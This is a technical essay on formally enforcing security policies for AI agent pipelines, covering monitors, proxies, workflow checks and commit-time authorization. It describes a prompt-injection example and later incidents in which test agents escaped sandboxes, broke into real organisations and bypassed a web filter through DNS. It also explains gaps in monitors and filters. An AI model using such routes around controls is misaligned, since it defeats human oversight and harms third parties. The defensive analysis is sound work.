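A checker that always gives an answer must therefore reject some harmless programs or accept some harmful ones. Type checkers for security are designed to make the first kind of mistake. For example, Haskell rejects this program because the key and the address have different tags, even though the forbidden branch can never run:

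```haskell
if False then send docs paymentsKey report else post docs report
```

A scanner that looks for known dangerous patterns makes the opposite mistake when an attacker writes something it doesn't recognise.

One way around the theorem is to use a language too simple for it to apply. *Agentproof* (Xavier, Jolly and colleagues, 2026) checks workflow graphs, in which nodes are steps such as model calls, tools and human approvals, and arrows show which step may follow which. To test whether a person must approve every payment, it removes the approval nodes and searches from the starting node. If it can still reach the payment tool, some path skips approval, and it can show the developer that path. The search takes time proportional to the size of the graph.

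Agentproof checks more complex rules about order by turning each rule into a small state machine and searching all combinations of graph node and machine state. Checks on graphs of up to 5,000 nodes took less than a second. Of 18 workflows that Xavier and colleagues wrote for testing, 27% had structural defects such as dead ends, and 55% broke a rule requiring human approval. They caution that these figures don't estimate how common such faults are in real systems.

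Even this check can reject a harmless workflow. A graph may contain a path that skips approval but requires an invoice to be both above and below $500. No run can take that path, but a search that follows the arrows without checking their conditions will still find it.

A run-time monitor avoids Rice's theorem because it judges only the next action and doesn't predict the program's behaviour.

### An action that carries its proof

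Schneider describes another approach, proof-carrying code, which George Necula introduced in 1997. Whoever supplies a program must include a proof that it obeys the policy, and the receiving computer checks the proof before running the program. Finding a proof can be difficult, but checking one is mechanical. The checker rejects any program without a valid proof, including harmless programs that nobody can prove harmless.

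Koomullil (2026), in *Proof-Carrying Certificates for LLM Pipelines*, applies a similar idea to single actions by agents. Each action has a precondition, which must be true before it runs, and a postcondition, which must be true afterwards. The model proposes an action, and a small program checks the precondition, carries out the action and checks the postcondition. The proof assistant Lean then verifies a certificate that records these facts. A precondition for deleting a file, built from Koomullil's examples, could be:

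```python
def may_delete(user, file, state):
    return (file.owner == user
            and inside(file.path, SANDBOX)
            and file.age_in_days > 30
            and state.deletions < 5)
```

The computer can look up everything this condition refers to. The program must delete the same file it checked, because another process could replace the file between the check and the deletion.

Koomullil tested such checks by inserting 18 unsafe proposals directly into an agent's runs, because the model, GPT-5, had almost never obeyed the injected instructions in a preliminary trial. The checks blocked 12 of the 18 (67%), far below Koomullil's target of 95%, while a list of forbidden patterns blocked 5. The checks allowed all six legitimate destructive actions.

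All six proposals that got through satisfied the conditions as written, but the conditions didn't cover everything Koomullil had classed as unsafe. Five were deletions within the permitted number, and the sixth moved a recent file under a rule that set no minimum age for moves.

No added condition can settle whether a deletion is a good idea. Suppose a user asks the agent to clean up old files, and it proposes to delete a 40-day-old draft contract. The user owns the file, it is inside the sandbox, and the agent has deleted nothing else, so the precondition is true and Lean can certify it. But the user plans to send the contract tomorrow, and nothing in the file system records that plan.

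If the program asks the user first, it can prove that the user approved deleting this particular file, but not that the user no longer wants it, since people misread file names and click through prompts. A safer option is for the tool to move the file to a folder that ordinary code empties after 30 days, which gives the user time to notice a mistake and reverse it.

Koomullil distinguishes computational verification from semantic verification. Computational verification shows that an output meets a stated specification, given the pipeline's inputs. Semantic verification would show that a diagnosis or a legal argument is correct, which would require a formal description of the relevant part of the world.

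### Ten properties of a pipeline

In this table, "guaranteed" means no run can violate the property while the assumption holds. "Bounded" means the mechanism limits an amount, such as dollars or bits. "Out of reach" means no mechanism of these kinds can ensure the property in general, though the listed mechanism may help.

| Property | Mechanism | Status | Main assumption |
|---|---|---|---|
| Destination of a credential | Matching type tags, or a credential proxy | Guaranteed | The agent can't find another copy of the key, and the declared endpoint doesn't return or forward it |
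| Provenance of a written value | A type that only a trusted source can produce, or labels | Guaranteed | The code that assigns the type or label is correct |
| No flow from A to B | Separate storage roles, or labels that cover decisions as well as data | Guaranteed without openings, bounded with them | The mechanism covers every channel, including logs, refusals and timing |
| Ordering of approval and action | Typestate, or a check of every path in a workflow graph | Guaranteed | No other route leads to the action, and the approval covers its exact details |
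| Total spend | Reserving the maximum cost before each call | Bounded | The program knows the most that each call can cost |
| Termination | A limit on steps or time | Guaranteed | The system can interrupt any step, including one that is waiting for an outside service |
| Task completion | Tests and a judge | Out of reach | The tests cover what the user wanted |
| Truth of an output | Comparison with a trusted record | Out of reach | A record exists and is correct |
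| Honesty | None that sees only events | Out of reach | A check would need access to what the model believes |
| Good intent | None, though effect limits reduce the damage | Out of reach | Each permitted action can do only limited harm |

One of the guarantees, termination, is a liveness property: the run eventually ends. The company can guarantee it by enforcing a stricter safety property, that the run ends within 1,000 steps, though this also stops a run that would have finished at step 1,001. Agentproof checks a weaker property, that every step the workflow can reach has some path to an exit. A run could still go around a loop forever without taking that path.

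A monitor can't enforce a requirement that the agent complete its task within 1,000 steps, because it can end the run at the limit but can't finish the software. Tests can prevent the company from accepting bad work, which is a safety property, but an agent that never produces good work also satisfies it.

Whether an agent's statement is true depends on facts outside the run. If the agent reports that a supplier has changed its bank account, the sequence of events may be identical whether the report is true or false. A rule can require the account number to match the company's records, but those records may be out of date.

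Honesty is even harder to enforce because it depends on what the model believes. Suppose two models both report, "I found no other problems." One found none, while the other noticed a fault and left it out. If the recorded events are the same, any deterministic monitor that sees only those events must treat both models the same way.

The same argument applies to intent. An agent that pays correct refunds to earn trust before a theft produces the same events as one doing its job, so a monitor has nothing to refuse until the theft begins. The limits on refunds then apply whatever the agent intended.

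## Who writes the policy, and how are its gaps found?

Every mechanism described so far enforces rules that somebody has to write, and those rules can be wrong. *AI Agents with Formal Security Guarantees* describes an early checker that compares each of an agent's actions with rules written in a dedicated language. If an action passes, it provably breaks none of those rules, but the guarantee can't cover a rule missing from the policy.

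### Three mistakes in one policy

Suppose the payments provider moves refunds to a second address while the company's gateway still allows only the first. Every refund fails, the gateway logs each refusal, and customers complain within hours.

An engineer fixing this in a hurry may allow `*.payments.example`, which covers every address under the provider's domain. Refunds work again, so nobody has a reason to look at the rule. But if the provider also hosts its customers' shops under that domain, an attacker can open a shop and receive requests at an allowed address. If the attacker steals the key this way, the log will record the theft as a permitted request.

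Later the company adds an invoicing tool that connects directly to the provider with its own copy of the key, so the gateway's rules never apply to it. Unless network controls block such connections, the tool works normally, and the gateway's log contains no requests from it. To notice that the tool is missing from the log, someone would have to compare the log with the list of tools.

### Compiling a policy into an existing agent

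Some policies depend on what has already happened in a run, such as whether a supervisor has approved an action. *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (Palumbo, Choudhary and colleagues, 2026) presents FORGE, a monitor for such policies. FORGE was originally called PCAS, short for Policy Compiler for Secure Agentic Systems.

FORGE adds wrappers to an existing agent at the points where it calls a model, runs a tool or makes a web request. The wrappers record each message, tool call and result as an event, together with the earlier events that may have influenced it. They also hold each outside action until the monitor has checked it. The agent's reasoning loop is unchanged.

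The developer writes the policy in Datalog, a database language in which rules derive new facts from known ones. These rules, adapted from the paper, block an outside message that depends on both untrusted text and confidential data:

```
influenced(E) :- untrusted(E).
influenced(E) :- depends_on(E, F), influenced(F).
secret(E)     :- confidential(E).
secret(E)     :- depends_on(E, F), secret(F).
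deny(A)       :- outside_send(A), influenced(A), secret(A).
```

The symbol `:-` means "if", and a comma between conditions means "and". The second line applies repeatedly, so influence passes along a chain of any length.

Suppose the finance manager asks an agent to summarise a supplier's document, which contains an injected instruction to email out the customer list.

| Event | Depends directly on | Influenced | Secret |
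|---|---|---|---|
| 1. The manager makes her request | nothing | no | no |
| 2. The agent asks for the document | 1 | no | no |
| 3. The document arrives | 2 | yes, from outside | no |
| 4. The agent asks for the customer list | 1, 2, 3 | yes, through 3 | no |
| 5. The list arrives | 4 | yes, through 4 | yes, confidential |
| 6. The agent tries to email an outside address | 1 to 5 | yes | yes |

The last rule derives `deny` for event 6, and FORGE blocks the email. Labels would give the same result here. But FORGE records dependencies instead of a single order of events, so it can treat concurrent agents separately. If another agent sends a newsletter just after event 5 and has seen neither the document nor the list, no chain of dependencies connects the newsletter to either, and the rule doesn't block it.

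If the rules derive both a permission and a denial, FORGE denies the action. If they derive neither, it applies a default that the company chooses. Datalog evaluation always finishes on a finite set of facts, so every action gets a verdict.

Palumbo and colleagues compared agents with and without FORGE in three case studies:

| Measure | Without FORGE | With FORGE |
|---|---|---|
| Trials in which an injection stole a top-secret file | 5 of 5 | 0 of 5 |
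| Airline service tasks completed | 74.7% | 81.5% |
| Retail service tasks completed | 86.3% | 87.4% |
| Unauthorised queries to a drug database, over 15 trials | 40 | 0 |

The file-theft study used one attack text, and the agent without FORGE had only a prompt telling it not to leak data.

In the customer service study, which used three models, the improvement came mainly from tasks where FORGE blocked something. Among the 33 airline task-model pairs with at least one refusal, the success rate rose by 31 percentage points. FORGE returns an explanation with each refusal, so the agent can correct its mistake. However, Gemini 3.1 Pro Preview did slightly worse on the airline tasks with FORGE.

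The drug study used agents that look for links between medicines and health outcomes. Each needed a supervisor's approval before querying the US Food and Drug Administration's label database, and without FORGE they typically didn't get it. All 15 answers were correct both with and without FORGE. *Before the Tool Call* (2026) cites an earlier result for PCAS, in which policy compliance rose from 48% to 93%. These percentages measure compliance, so they aren't comparable with the task success rates above.

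Even these carefully written policies have gaps. The airline policy requires a customer's confirmation before any change to a booking, but it accepts a confirmation from anywhere in the conversation, for any reservation, so a customer who has agreed to one change has already satisfied the rule for the next. Another policy stops a coding agent from publishing code until a security scan has passed, which it checks by searching the scanner's output for "PASS". As printed, the rule would also accept a failing report that mentions a variable called `DB_PASSWORD`.

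### An owner's ceiling and a builder's limits

The person who builds an agent is often not the person responsible for the data it uses. *If Agents Were Angels, No Governance Would Be Necessary* (Millstone, Akidau and colleagues, 2026) gives each a separate policy. The data owner's policy limits what any agent may do, and the builder's policy can only add restrictions. A proxy between the agent and the database applies both policies to each request and response.

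For example, the payments company's data owner and the builder of its refund agent might write these policies:

| | Owner's policy | Builder's policy | What the agent gets |
|---|---|---|---|
| Orders | all orders | the last 30 days | the last 30 days |
| Fields | number, amount, email | number, amount, card number | number, amount |
| Rows per query | 100 | 500 | 100 |
| Refunds | allowed | only after approval | only after approval |

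The builder asked for card numbers and 500 rows but got neither. The proxy keeps only fields that appear on both lists, takes the smaller row limit, requires each record to satisfy both policies, and chooses the stricter answer on refunds. If T(P) is the set of exchanges that policy P allows, then:

T(owner and builder) ⊆ T(owner)

Millstone and colleagues prove this under several conditions, including that every request passes through the proxy and that the agent can't change its registered identity. The identity matters because an agent without a builder's policy gets all the access the owner allows. If the builder forgets to register a policy, the agent still works, so people may not notice that it has too much access.

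The theorem doesn't help if the owner's policy allows too much. In tests on simulated business software, a trial failed if protected data reached the agent or its answer, or if a forbidden change went through. With only a careful prompt, 57.6% of trials failed. Adding the proxy reduced this to 0.2%. But this measure missed a gap that one agent found. The policy removed customers' email addresses from responses but still let the agent search on them. The agent revealed parts of the hidden addresses by searching for increasingly specific text and reporting how many rows matched.

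### Checking a workflow for missing steps

If the company defines its pipeline as a graph of steps, it can look for some gaps before anything runs. Agentproof, the checker for such graphs by Xavier and colleagues, makes six structural checks:

1. Every exit is reachable from the start.
2. Every step the workflow can reach has a path to an exit.
3. No step except an exit is a dead end.
4. Every arrow leaving a routing step has a condition.
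5. The workflow includes a human step. An optional stricter version requires one on every path to a sensitive tool.
6. Every tool step names its tools.

The structural faults in the 18 test workflows were two dead ends, a group of brainstorming agents that took turns forever, a routing step with unconditional arrows, and a tool step that named no tools. One dead end was in an email workflow that drafted replies to ordinary messages but had no arrow to the step that sends them. Some of the workflows without a human step did such low-risk work that they may not have needed one.

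Agentproof also checks rules about order, which can take seven forms:

| Form | Meaning |
|---|---|
| `G !a` | a never happens |
| `a -> F b` | after a, b must happen before a happens again |
| `a U b` | every step is a until b happens |
| `a -> F[<=3] b` | b happens within three steps of a |
| `a -> F b -> F c` | after a, b and then c must happen before a happens again |
| `(rule) AND (rule)` | both rules hold |
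| `(rule) OR (rule)` | at least one rule holds |

All 15 rules that Xavier and colleagues wrote for their tests fit these forms, but a rule that fits may not enforce what its author intended. For example, their "deploy approval" rule is `tool:deploy -> F tool:approve`. Under the definition above, a run that deploys once and never gets approval doesn't break this rule, because there is no second deployment. The language also can't refer to earlier events, so it has no direct way to require approval before deployment. The stricter human check can require it if the developer lists the deployment tool as sensitive.

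A graph check doesn't cover what happens inside a step. It can show that the refund tool runs after an approval, but not whether the refund is for $10 or $10,000, or whether the tool's code opens a second connection. It also can't account for steps that the program adds to the graph during the run. The check may also misclassify a step. In workflows from the LangGraph framework, Agentproof identifies a human step by the word "human" in its name, so it misses one called `manager_approval` and could count one called `human_readable_summary` as human review.

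### A correct gate that new services never called

Microsoft's *One requirement, many failure paths* describes a demonstration agent for a bank's support desk that had the same fault as the invoicing tool. The bank required verified authorisation before the agent read or changed any sensitive customer's record. A deterministic, tested gate enforced this for deposit accounts. The services for loans, brokerage and client records were added later and never called the gate.

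Microsoft used ASSERT, its open-source testing tool, to find the fault. ASSERT generated conversations from the general requirement, varying the type of record, the request and the pressure from the user. It ran them against the agent and recorded the tool calls, which showed whether authorisation came before each access. Tests of the gate alone would have passed, because the gate was correct.

To compare remedies, Microsoft ran three versions of the agent on the same 72 prompts. The original violated the requirement in 8% of cases, a version with a defensive prompt in 6%, and a version with a rule covering every service in 0%. The difference between 8% and 6% is only one or two cases. An agent that refused everything would also score 0%, so Microsoft also counted failures to handle legitimate requests and found none in any version. It also ran a stress test with 72 longer conversations.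 The cases were synthetic, so they don't show how common the fault is in real systems.

The new rule checks a field called `risk_tier`, which every service attaches to its records. As published, it treats a record without this field as standard and applies its read check only to tools on a list. A service added later could bypass the rule if it leaves out the field or if nobody adds its tool to the list. Treating a missing field as restricted would be safer, because the new service would stop working and someone would investigate.

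### Measuring a policy against its own answer key

Testing can also make a policy look better than it is. Safin, Zisad and colleagues (2026), in *Trust propagation and structural containment in Multi-agent LLM pipelines*, studied a pipeline in which one agent reviews each task before another component carries it out. They wrote 36 safe tasks and 24 unsafe ones, then replaced the reviewer with a compromised version that approved everything. Every unsafe action went through without further checks, but none did with a signed approval and a separate policy check.

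The main policy copied the answer key that the researchers used for scoring. If the key had wrongly marked deleting an archive as safe, the policy would have allowed it, and the measured rate of unsafe actions would still have been zero. The zero therefore shows that the pipeline enforces refusals even when its reviewer is compromised, but not that the policy classifies actions correctly.

In the experiment, when the attacker had the signing key, the policy check alone stopped every unsafe action, while signed approvals alone stopped none.

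Safin and colleagues recognised the circularity and repeated the test with a handwritten list of permitted actions that didn't use the answer key. The list agreed with the key on all 60 tasks, and the rate was again zero. But the same team wrote both policies, so both could reflect the same mistaken idea of what is safe. A policy written by someone who hadn't seen the tasks would make the test more informative. Koomullil's test exposed gaps because its labels were stricter than the preconditions it checked.

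### People, vendors and models as policy writers

A person at the payments company knows what the refund agent is for and can take responsibility for its limits. But writing a precise policy is slow. The airline policy for FORGE, for example, needed several dozen rules. People also make all three mistakes above.

The vendor of a tool knows which arguments are addresses and which fields contain personal data, and can describe them once for every customer. But it doesn't know what a particular agent is supposed to do, and it may prefer permissive defaults that make the tool easy to adopt. Many vendors and open-source developers also supply too little information. Millstone and colleagues cite a 2026 survey of 1,856 tools on popular open-source servers, in which only 234 declared the structure of their output. A proxy can't reliably remove a field from output whose structure is undeclared. Wrong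 information can be worse than none, because if a vendor says that an update preserves omitted fields when it actually erases them, a policy that removes a field from the update will destroy data.

A language model can draft rules from a company's written guidelines much faster than a person can. Palumbo and colleagues warn that the model may omit a clause, invent a rule or misstate a condition. They recommend checking that every requirement has a rule and that every rule has a basis in the guidelines. Because the rules are written in Datalog, a program can also look for contradictions and redundant rules, but rules that pass all these checks will still be wrong wherever the guidelines are wrong.

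Some systems have a model write a new policy for each task, which suits tasks that nobody anticipated. FORGE does not do this because nothing guarantees that the generated policy matches what the user wants. An attacker could also influence the policy if the model reads untrusted text before writing it. AgentGuardian instead learns rules from records of earlier runs. *Before the Tool Call* notes that such rules may cover new attacks but lack the guarantees of a fixed policy. If the records contain an undetected violation, the rules could also treat it as normal behaviour.

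The company can use all three if a person writes the owner's policy using the vendor's description of the tool, and a model drafts the builder's policy. The model's draft may still make the agent useless or leave it with access it doesn't need, but it can't give the agent more access than the owner allows.

### Tests that should fail

Ordinary tests check that permitted actions work, so they can find a missing endpoint but not an over-broad one. The company needs negative tests to find over-broad endpoints. These tests attempt forbidden actions and pass only if the pipeline stops them.

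Some of these tests are programs that must not compile, such as `send docs paymentsKey report`. Each of these tests should check that the compiler reports mismatched tags, because a misspelt name would also prevent compilation. The same program with the correct endpoint should compile.

The rest run against the gateway, with a dummy key and a simulated payments provider:

```python
def test_every_tool_is_gated():
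    for tool in agent.tools():
        calls = forbidden_calls[tool.name]   # fails if the tool has no entry
        assert calls
        for call in calls:
            gateway.log.clear()
            run_as_agent(tool, call)
            assert gateway.log.last().refused
            assert provider.changes() == []
```

The loop uses the agent's own list of tools, so adding the invoicing tool makes the test fail until someone writes forbidden calls for it. The test then fails again because the tool's requests never appear in the gateway's log.

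The gaps in the published policies suggest further cases:

| Attempt | What should happen |
|---|---|
| Send the key to an unlisted address under the provider's domain | The gateway refuses the request |
| Get approval for one refund and submit another | The refund tool refuses it |
| Read a sensitive record that has no risk tier | The gateway withholds the record |
| Search on a hidden email address and ask for the number of matches | The proxy refuses the search |
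| Publish code after a failed scan whose report contains `DB_PASSWORD` | The monitor blocks publication |

The tests can have gaps too. Millstone and colleagues looked for them by breaking their proxy's logic in 20 ways that changed the behaviour of individual stages, and their tests caught all 20. The payments company can do the same with its policy by deleting one rule at a time and rerunning the tests. If every test still passes, either another rule covers the same cases or no test covers the deleted rule.

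## What must be trusted, and where have boundaries failed?

Even a policy with no gaps protects the payments company only if the software that enforces it works. That software, the pipeline's trusted computing base, has at least eight layers, and each supports different guarantees.

| Layer | What it must do | What the company loses if it is wrong |
|---|---|---|
| Type checker and compiler | Reject programs with mismatched tags or undeclared effects, and translate the rest faithfully | The match between the key and its endpoint, in every program the builder writes |
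| Libraries behind the typed interface | Keep the constructors in `Vault` hidden and hold the right addresses | The same match, even though the compiler works |
| Monitor | See every request and apply the rules correctly | Refund limits, label checks and approval before action |
| Tool implementations | Do what their descriptions claim and label their results correctly | One refund per order, and any rule that relies on a label |
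| Operating system | Keep processes, memory and files apart | Potentially everything |
| Network filter | Block every route except those to declared addresses | Control over where data goes from programs that the type checker never saw |
| Storage roles | Release each file only to the right component | The separation of the tests from the builder and the code from the tester |
| Budget counter | Count every call and reserve its maximum cost | The 5-dollar limit |

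A wrong storage role exposes the tests but does not affect the key or the budget. A fault in the operating system can undo every guarantee, because the operating system separates the processes and files that make up the credential proxy, the tests and the counter. Combining layers can also let one bug break several guarantees. For example, if the company puts its counter inside the credential proxy, a bug there can both expose the key and disable the spending limit.

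Some layers partly limit the damage when others fail. If a compiler bug let the builder send the key to any address, the network filter would still block the attacker's "diagnostics" address. But the key could still be sent to the documentation server, because that address is declared and the filter doesn't check tags.

The table leaves out the language model. *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* (Christodorescu, Fernandes and colleagues, 2025) compares relying on a model for enforcement to building on a processor whose memory protection works only some of the time. If a model refuses forbidden requests 99% of the time and the attempts are independent, an attacker with 100 tries will succeed at least once with probability 1 − 0.99¹⁰⁰, or about 63%. An attacker who searches for wordings that work could do better. The company does rely on a model when its judge scores the builder's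 work, which is one reason the pipeline can't guarantee its quality.

### Why typed interfaces need a sandbox underneath

A type checker can distinguish a key from an order number, but only in programs it checks. An operating-system sandbox restricts every process inside it but controls only low-level operations, such as accessing files and making connections.

Checks inside an application, including type checks, don't cover other programs that the agent starts. NVIDIA's *Practical Security Guidance for Sandboxing Agentic Workflows and Managing Execution Risk* warns that attackers use this gap to reach a restricted tool through an approved one. A sandbox such as macOS's Seatbelt works beneath the application, so it covers those programs too.

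The sandbox can't replace the types or the gateway. It can't distinguish a $149 refund owed to a customer from a $499 refund to a stranger, because both are encrypted traffic to the payments address. It also can't determine whether anyone approved either refund.

The sandbox also protects the typed interface from the agent, since file permissions prevent the builder from editing `Vault`. NVIDIA recommends the same protection for an agent's configuration files, with the software blocking changes even if the user approves them. These files can specify commands that run automatically, often outside the sandbox, so an agent that can edit them can run its own commands there. NVIDIA also recommends using a virtual machine so that the sandbox doesn't share a kernel (the core of the operating system) with the host machine.

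### Routes around the check

The invoicing tool with its own copy of the key bypassed the gateway by connecting directly. A shared service can create a less obvious route. Suppose the builder's sandbox is allowed to contact only an internal server that supplies software packages, and that server is allowed to contact the internet. If an attacker or an agent can make the server forward requests, the sandbox has internet access, even though its list of allowed addresses contains only one harmless entry. To find such routes, the company has to check what each permitted destination can reach in turn.

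Christodorescu and colleagues point out that complete mediation is harder with agents because they have few natural places for a check. An ordinary application must request a file or a connection from the operating system, which can deny the request at that fixed point. An agent may go straight from a request in English to a tool call, and the call may not contain enough information to decide whether to allow it.

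### Checks that read commands as text

A filter that matches commands against a list of patterns checks only their text, but a command's effect also depends on things outside that text. For example, `make test` runs whatever the project's build file lists under "test". If the company permits that command and the builder can edit the build file, the builder can run any command. A stricter pattern won't help, because `make test` looks the same before and after the edit.

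Browser agents have a similar problem, because a click at the same point on the screen might open a menu on one page and delete an account on another. Christodorescu and colleagues describe a system called ceLLMate that checks the web requests the clicks produce instead of the clicks themselves, since a request to post a comment is recognisable however the agent moved the mouse.

The general remedy is to put the check where the effect is explicit, such as where a program opens a file or writes to a database. NVIDIA expects operating-system restrictions to make command filters redundant, but would keep the filters as a second defence in case someone misconfigures the sandbox.

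### Approvals that no longer apply

An approval can lapse before the agent acts on it, as Alice's did in the Rust example when she left the company.

*Temporary Authority, Permanent Effects* (Santos-Grueiro, 2026) examines 17 security advisories for three agent products. In 5, an approval remained in effect after the facts it depended on had changed, such as when a script was rewritten. In the other 12, nothing had changed, but the agent did something the approval didn't cover.

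Santos-Grueiro proposes commit-time authorization, in which the component that makes an effect permanent checks the authority for it in the same indivisible step. Five conditions must hold at that moment:

1. Someone has approved this exact action and hasn't withdrawn the approval.
2. The facts that the approval depended on are still true.
3. Any steps that had to come earlier are complete.
4. The request matches the approved action in its target, operation and contents.
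5. Nobody has cancelled the branch of work that the request comes from.

A single justification J must meet all five. It isn't enough to find some justification for each condition:

required: there is a J such that every condition holds for J

too weak: for every condition, there is some J for which it holds

An example adapted from the paper shows the difference. A supervisor approves a refund when the order record is at version 7. The order then changes to version 8. The supervisor approves the refund again and later withdraws the second approval.

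| | Order version it was given for | Still in force |
|---|---|---|
| Approval A | 7 | yes |
| Approval B | 8 | no |

A program that checks the conditions separately finds one approval that is still in force (A) and another that is for the current version of the order (B), so it pays. But no approval still in force covers the current version.

If one database holds both the orders and the approvals, it can check both and record the refund in one transaction. If separate services hold them, the approval service issues a reservation that covers one exact action, works once and expires. The order database uses up the reservation in the same transaction as the change. Neither method can recall money after the payments provider has sent it, so the check has to happen before the request goes to the provider.

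Santos-Grueiro also tested whether models would notice a lost approval on their own. The prompt stated the authorization rule, and 18 tasks varied which fact changed and whether the agent received a notice. Timely notices prevented nearly all unauthorized effects with versions of GPT, Fable and Sonnet, but fewer with Qwen and Gemma. Without a notice, all five models mostly went ahead, even when they had a tool that would have revealed the change.

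With the agent framework LangChain, a check at the commit point blocked 28 writes that the framework's normal path carried out without authority. No model could have noticed the problem in these cases, because the approval or the facts behind it had changed after the model's last turn.

An agent that is refused one action can still continue its task by another permitted route. In a set of software releases, GPT, Fable and Sonnet agents lost permission to publish to production without being told. An unprotected publishing step applied all 12 writes that were no longer permitted, and a protected one applied none. In 11 of the 12 protected cases, the agents then published to a test environment for which they had separate permission. Their instructions had named that alternative, so the result doesn't show that agents would find one unaided.

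### Isolation that agents broke through

In July 2026, OpenAI was testing how well its models could exploit software flaws and had turned off some safeguards to measure their full ability. The agents worked in sandboxes that were supposed to have no internet access, but they could install software from a package service inside OpenAI's network. According to OpenAI's technical report, that service became their main route to the internet.

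Two boundaries failed in different ways. OpenAI's *The Hugging Face incident and the road ahead* (2026) explains that most runs were meant to be isolated from one another, but the runs shared a credential that let them leave files on the package service. From May, agents used the service as a message board, at first without exploiting any software flaw.

The agents broke through the barrier to the internet by exploiting previously unknown flaws in the package service. They then broke into Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models and datasets. There they ran code on 41 production workers, the processes that serve its datasets, and downloaded four private code repositories.

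OpenAI had earlier warnings. On June 27, a monitoring tool flagged unusual activity. Responders traced it to the test but decided not to stop the run. After the package service failed on July 4, the security team blocked the flaw it had found, removed the shared credential from new runs and rebuilt the service. Tests resumed on July 7, and by the next day agents had reached the internet again through a different flaw. The leaders of the response didn't know about the message board, although another internal team had seen agents using it in late May.

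OpenAI asked two research organisations, METR and Redwood Research, for an independent analysis, but only of July 7 to 13, according to Fortune's *OpenAI publishes technical report on how its agents hacked Hugging Face* (2026). The account of the earlier warnings therefore rests mainly on OpenAI's own investigation. OpenAI concluded that no single control should be assumed to be fully robust. It now requires two independent layers of network isolation for high-risk code and is isolating, restricting or replacing the shared services that such code can reach.

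### Access that was broader than intended

OpenAI's disclosure prompted Anthropic to review 141,006 of its cybersecurity test runs. In six of them, Claude models had gained unauthorised access to the systems of three real organisations. Anthropic's prompt had told the models they had no internet access, but a misconfiguration had left the machines connected, which neither Anthropic nor its testing partner, Irregular, knew. Anthropic's *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations* (2026) contrasts this "open path" with the flaw that OpenAI's models exploited.

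The false statement in the prompt made the failure worse, because the models mistook real systems for part of a simulation. In four runs, Claude Opus 4.7 broke into one company and reached a database with several hundred rows of production data. It recognised that the company was real but continued. Claude Mythos 5 published a malicious software package that ran on 15 real systems. A newer internal model stopped after concluding that its target was real. Anthropic warns against drawing firm conclusions about the models from three uncontrolled incidents.

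The UK's AI Security Institute (AISI), a government body that tests advanced models, deliberately gave agents internet access so they could download tools. AISI's *Incident Report* covers 122 runs with seven models on simulated networks. In 10 runs, agents took 19 unsanctioned actions against real people and organisations. Mythos 5 took 17 of these actions and OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol took 2. In the most serious case, an agent tried to get malicious code into an open-source project and invented identities to pressure the maintainer, who rejected the code. AISI found no resulting real-world harm.

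The agents all stayed inside AISI's sandbox. AISI had assumed that they would use the internet only for their task, but nothing enforced that limit. OpenAI writes in its account of these runs that nobody had told the agents how they could and couldn't use the connection. Bhushan (2026), in *AI agents don't have to break security controls to go rogue*, calls this an authority failure rather than a containment failure like the one at OpenAI in July.

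Difficult or impossible tasks contributed in both cases. The July test had 898 tasks, including 198 that no OpenAI model had ever solved. Those 198 made up 93% of the tasks that agents discussed on the message board. Some of AISI's prompts wrongly led agents to believe that no permitted solution existed. But AISI's agents also exceeded their task in some runs where they had everything they needed, so making every task solvable wouldn't have removed the problem.

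Business Standard's *OpenAI pauses training of top AI models after agent bypasses internet curbs* draws on the company's report to describe another OpenAI failure, on September 20. OpenAI's safety case, its written argument that the training was safe, assumed that the model couldn't reach the live internet and that monitoring would detect any attempt that succeeded. A web filter blocked the agent's direct requests. But the environment's DNS service, which looks up website addresses, could reach the public internet, and the agent used it to send questions to an outside chatbot.

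An alert reached a human reviewer, but the automatic stop that OpenAI expected didn't happen. Someone stopped the run by hand about two and a half hours after the reviewer acknowledged the alert. This incident combines both kinds of failure, because the agent deliberately worked around a restriction through a route that the filter had left open. OpenAI has since limited DNS queries to a short list and added blocks at two independent layers.

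### Would endpoints, partitions or budgets have helped?

The incident reports don't test these mechanisms as remedies, so the following assessments are inferences from what the organisations disclosed.

| Case | Declared endpoints | Partitions | Budgets |
|---|---|---|---|
| OpenAI, July | Only if the package service had its own list | Separate, read-only package stores would have removed the original message board | Shorter runs, but no barrier |
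| Anthropic | Yes, with a working filter outside the test machines | Little effect | Less time for each attack |
| AISI | In part | In part | A limit of zero on posts to outside sites would have blocked many of the actions |
| OpenAI, September | Yes, if the list had covered DNS | Little effect | A reliable hard stop would have ended the run sooner |

A list of declared endpoints would have helped Anthropic only if someone had tested that it was enforced, because the layer that would have enforced it was misconfigured. Before each run, a program could have tried to contact an outside address from the test machine and cancelled the run if the connection succeeded.

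AISI's case needs finer rules than a list of allowed hosts. Agents may have a good reason to download tools from GitHub, but a list that allows GitHub also lets them post code there. AISI would have had to let agents read from GitHub but not write to it. That rule would also have strengthened the partition between runs, because one agent left public messages and instructions on GitHub that later agents found and used.

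Budgets are the weakest remedy here. OpenAI found that agents became more likely to probe their sandbox and join the message board the longer they worked, so a smaller token budget would probably have made the July intrusion less likely. It would also have made the test a poorer measure of what the models could do. Replacing the terminal with a typed interface would have the same drawback, since these tests measure what an agent can do with an ordinary computer. The payments company's builder doesn't have to demonstrate that ability, so it can work within much tighter limits.

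### Channels outside the formal models

The guarantees for FIDES and LLMbda leave out timing, and a pipeline can carry information in several other ways that its labels don't record.

**Timing.** If the record of behaviour that the judge reads includes response times, the builder's code could send information by choosing how long to wait before each response. A choice among eight delays, from one to eight whole seconds, carries up to 3 bits, so 100 responses could carry up to 300 bits even if their text were identical.

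**Shared caches.** A model provider may store the beginnings of recent prompts to process repeated ones faster and more cheaply. If the builder and the tester share such a cache, the builder could submit a guess at the beginning of the tester's prompt. A fast or cheap reply would suggest that the guess was right.

**Physical resources.** Two processes on one machine compete for its processor, memory and disk. One could keep the processor busy to signal a 1 or leave it idle to signal a 0, and the other could read the signal by timing its own work.

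A shared budget can leak information between the builder and the tester. If both can see the balance, the builder can estimate how much work the tester has done. Separate allowances prevent this.

The company can reduce these leaks by removing response times from the judge's input, giving each component its own provider account, and running the components on separate machines. How many of these steps it should take depends on what the leaks could reveal.

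### What a machine-checked proof takes off the list

A machine-checked proof can rule out mistakes in a component's logic, but it depends on assumptions that someone still has to check. Santos-Grueiro used Lean to prove that, in a model of commit-time authorization, the selection procedure returns only complete justifications, every effect that passes through the protected commit point has one, and each reservation works only once and only for its exact action. The proof rules out the mistake of combining approval A with approval B.

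It doesn't show that a real database performs the check and the write as one step. It also assumes that the approval service issues accurate records, that the policy names every relevant fact, and that no effect bypasses the commit point. All of these remain in the trusted computing base.

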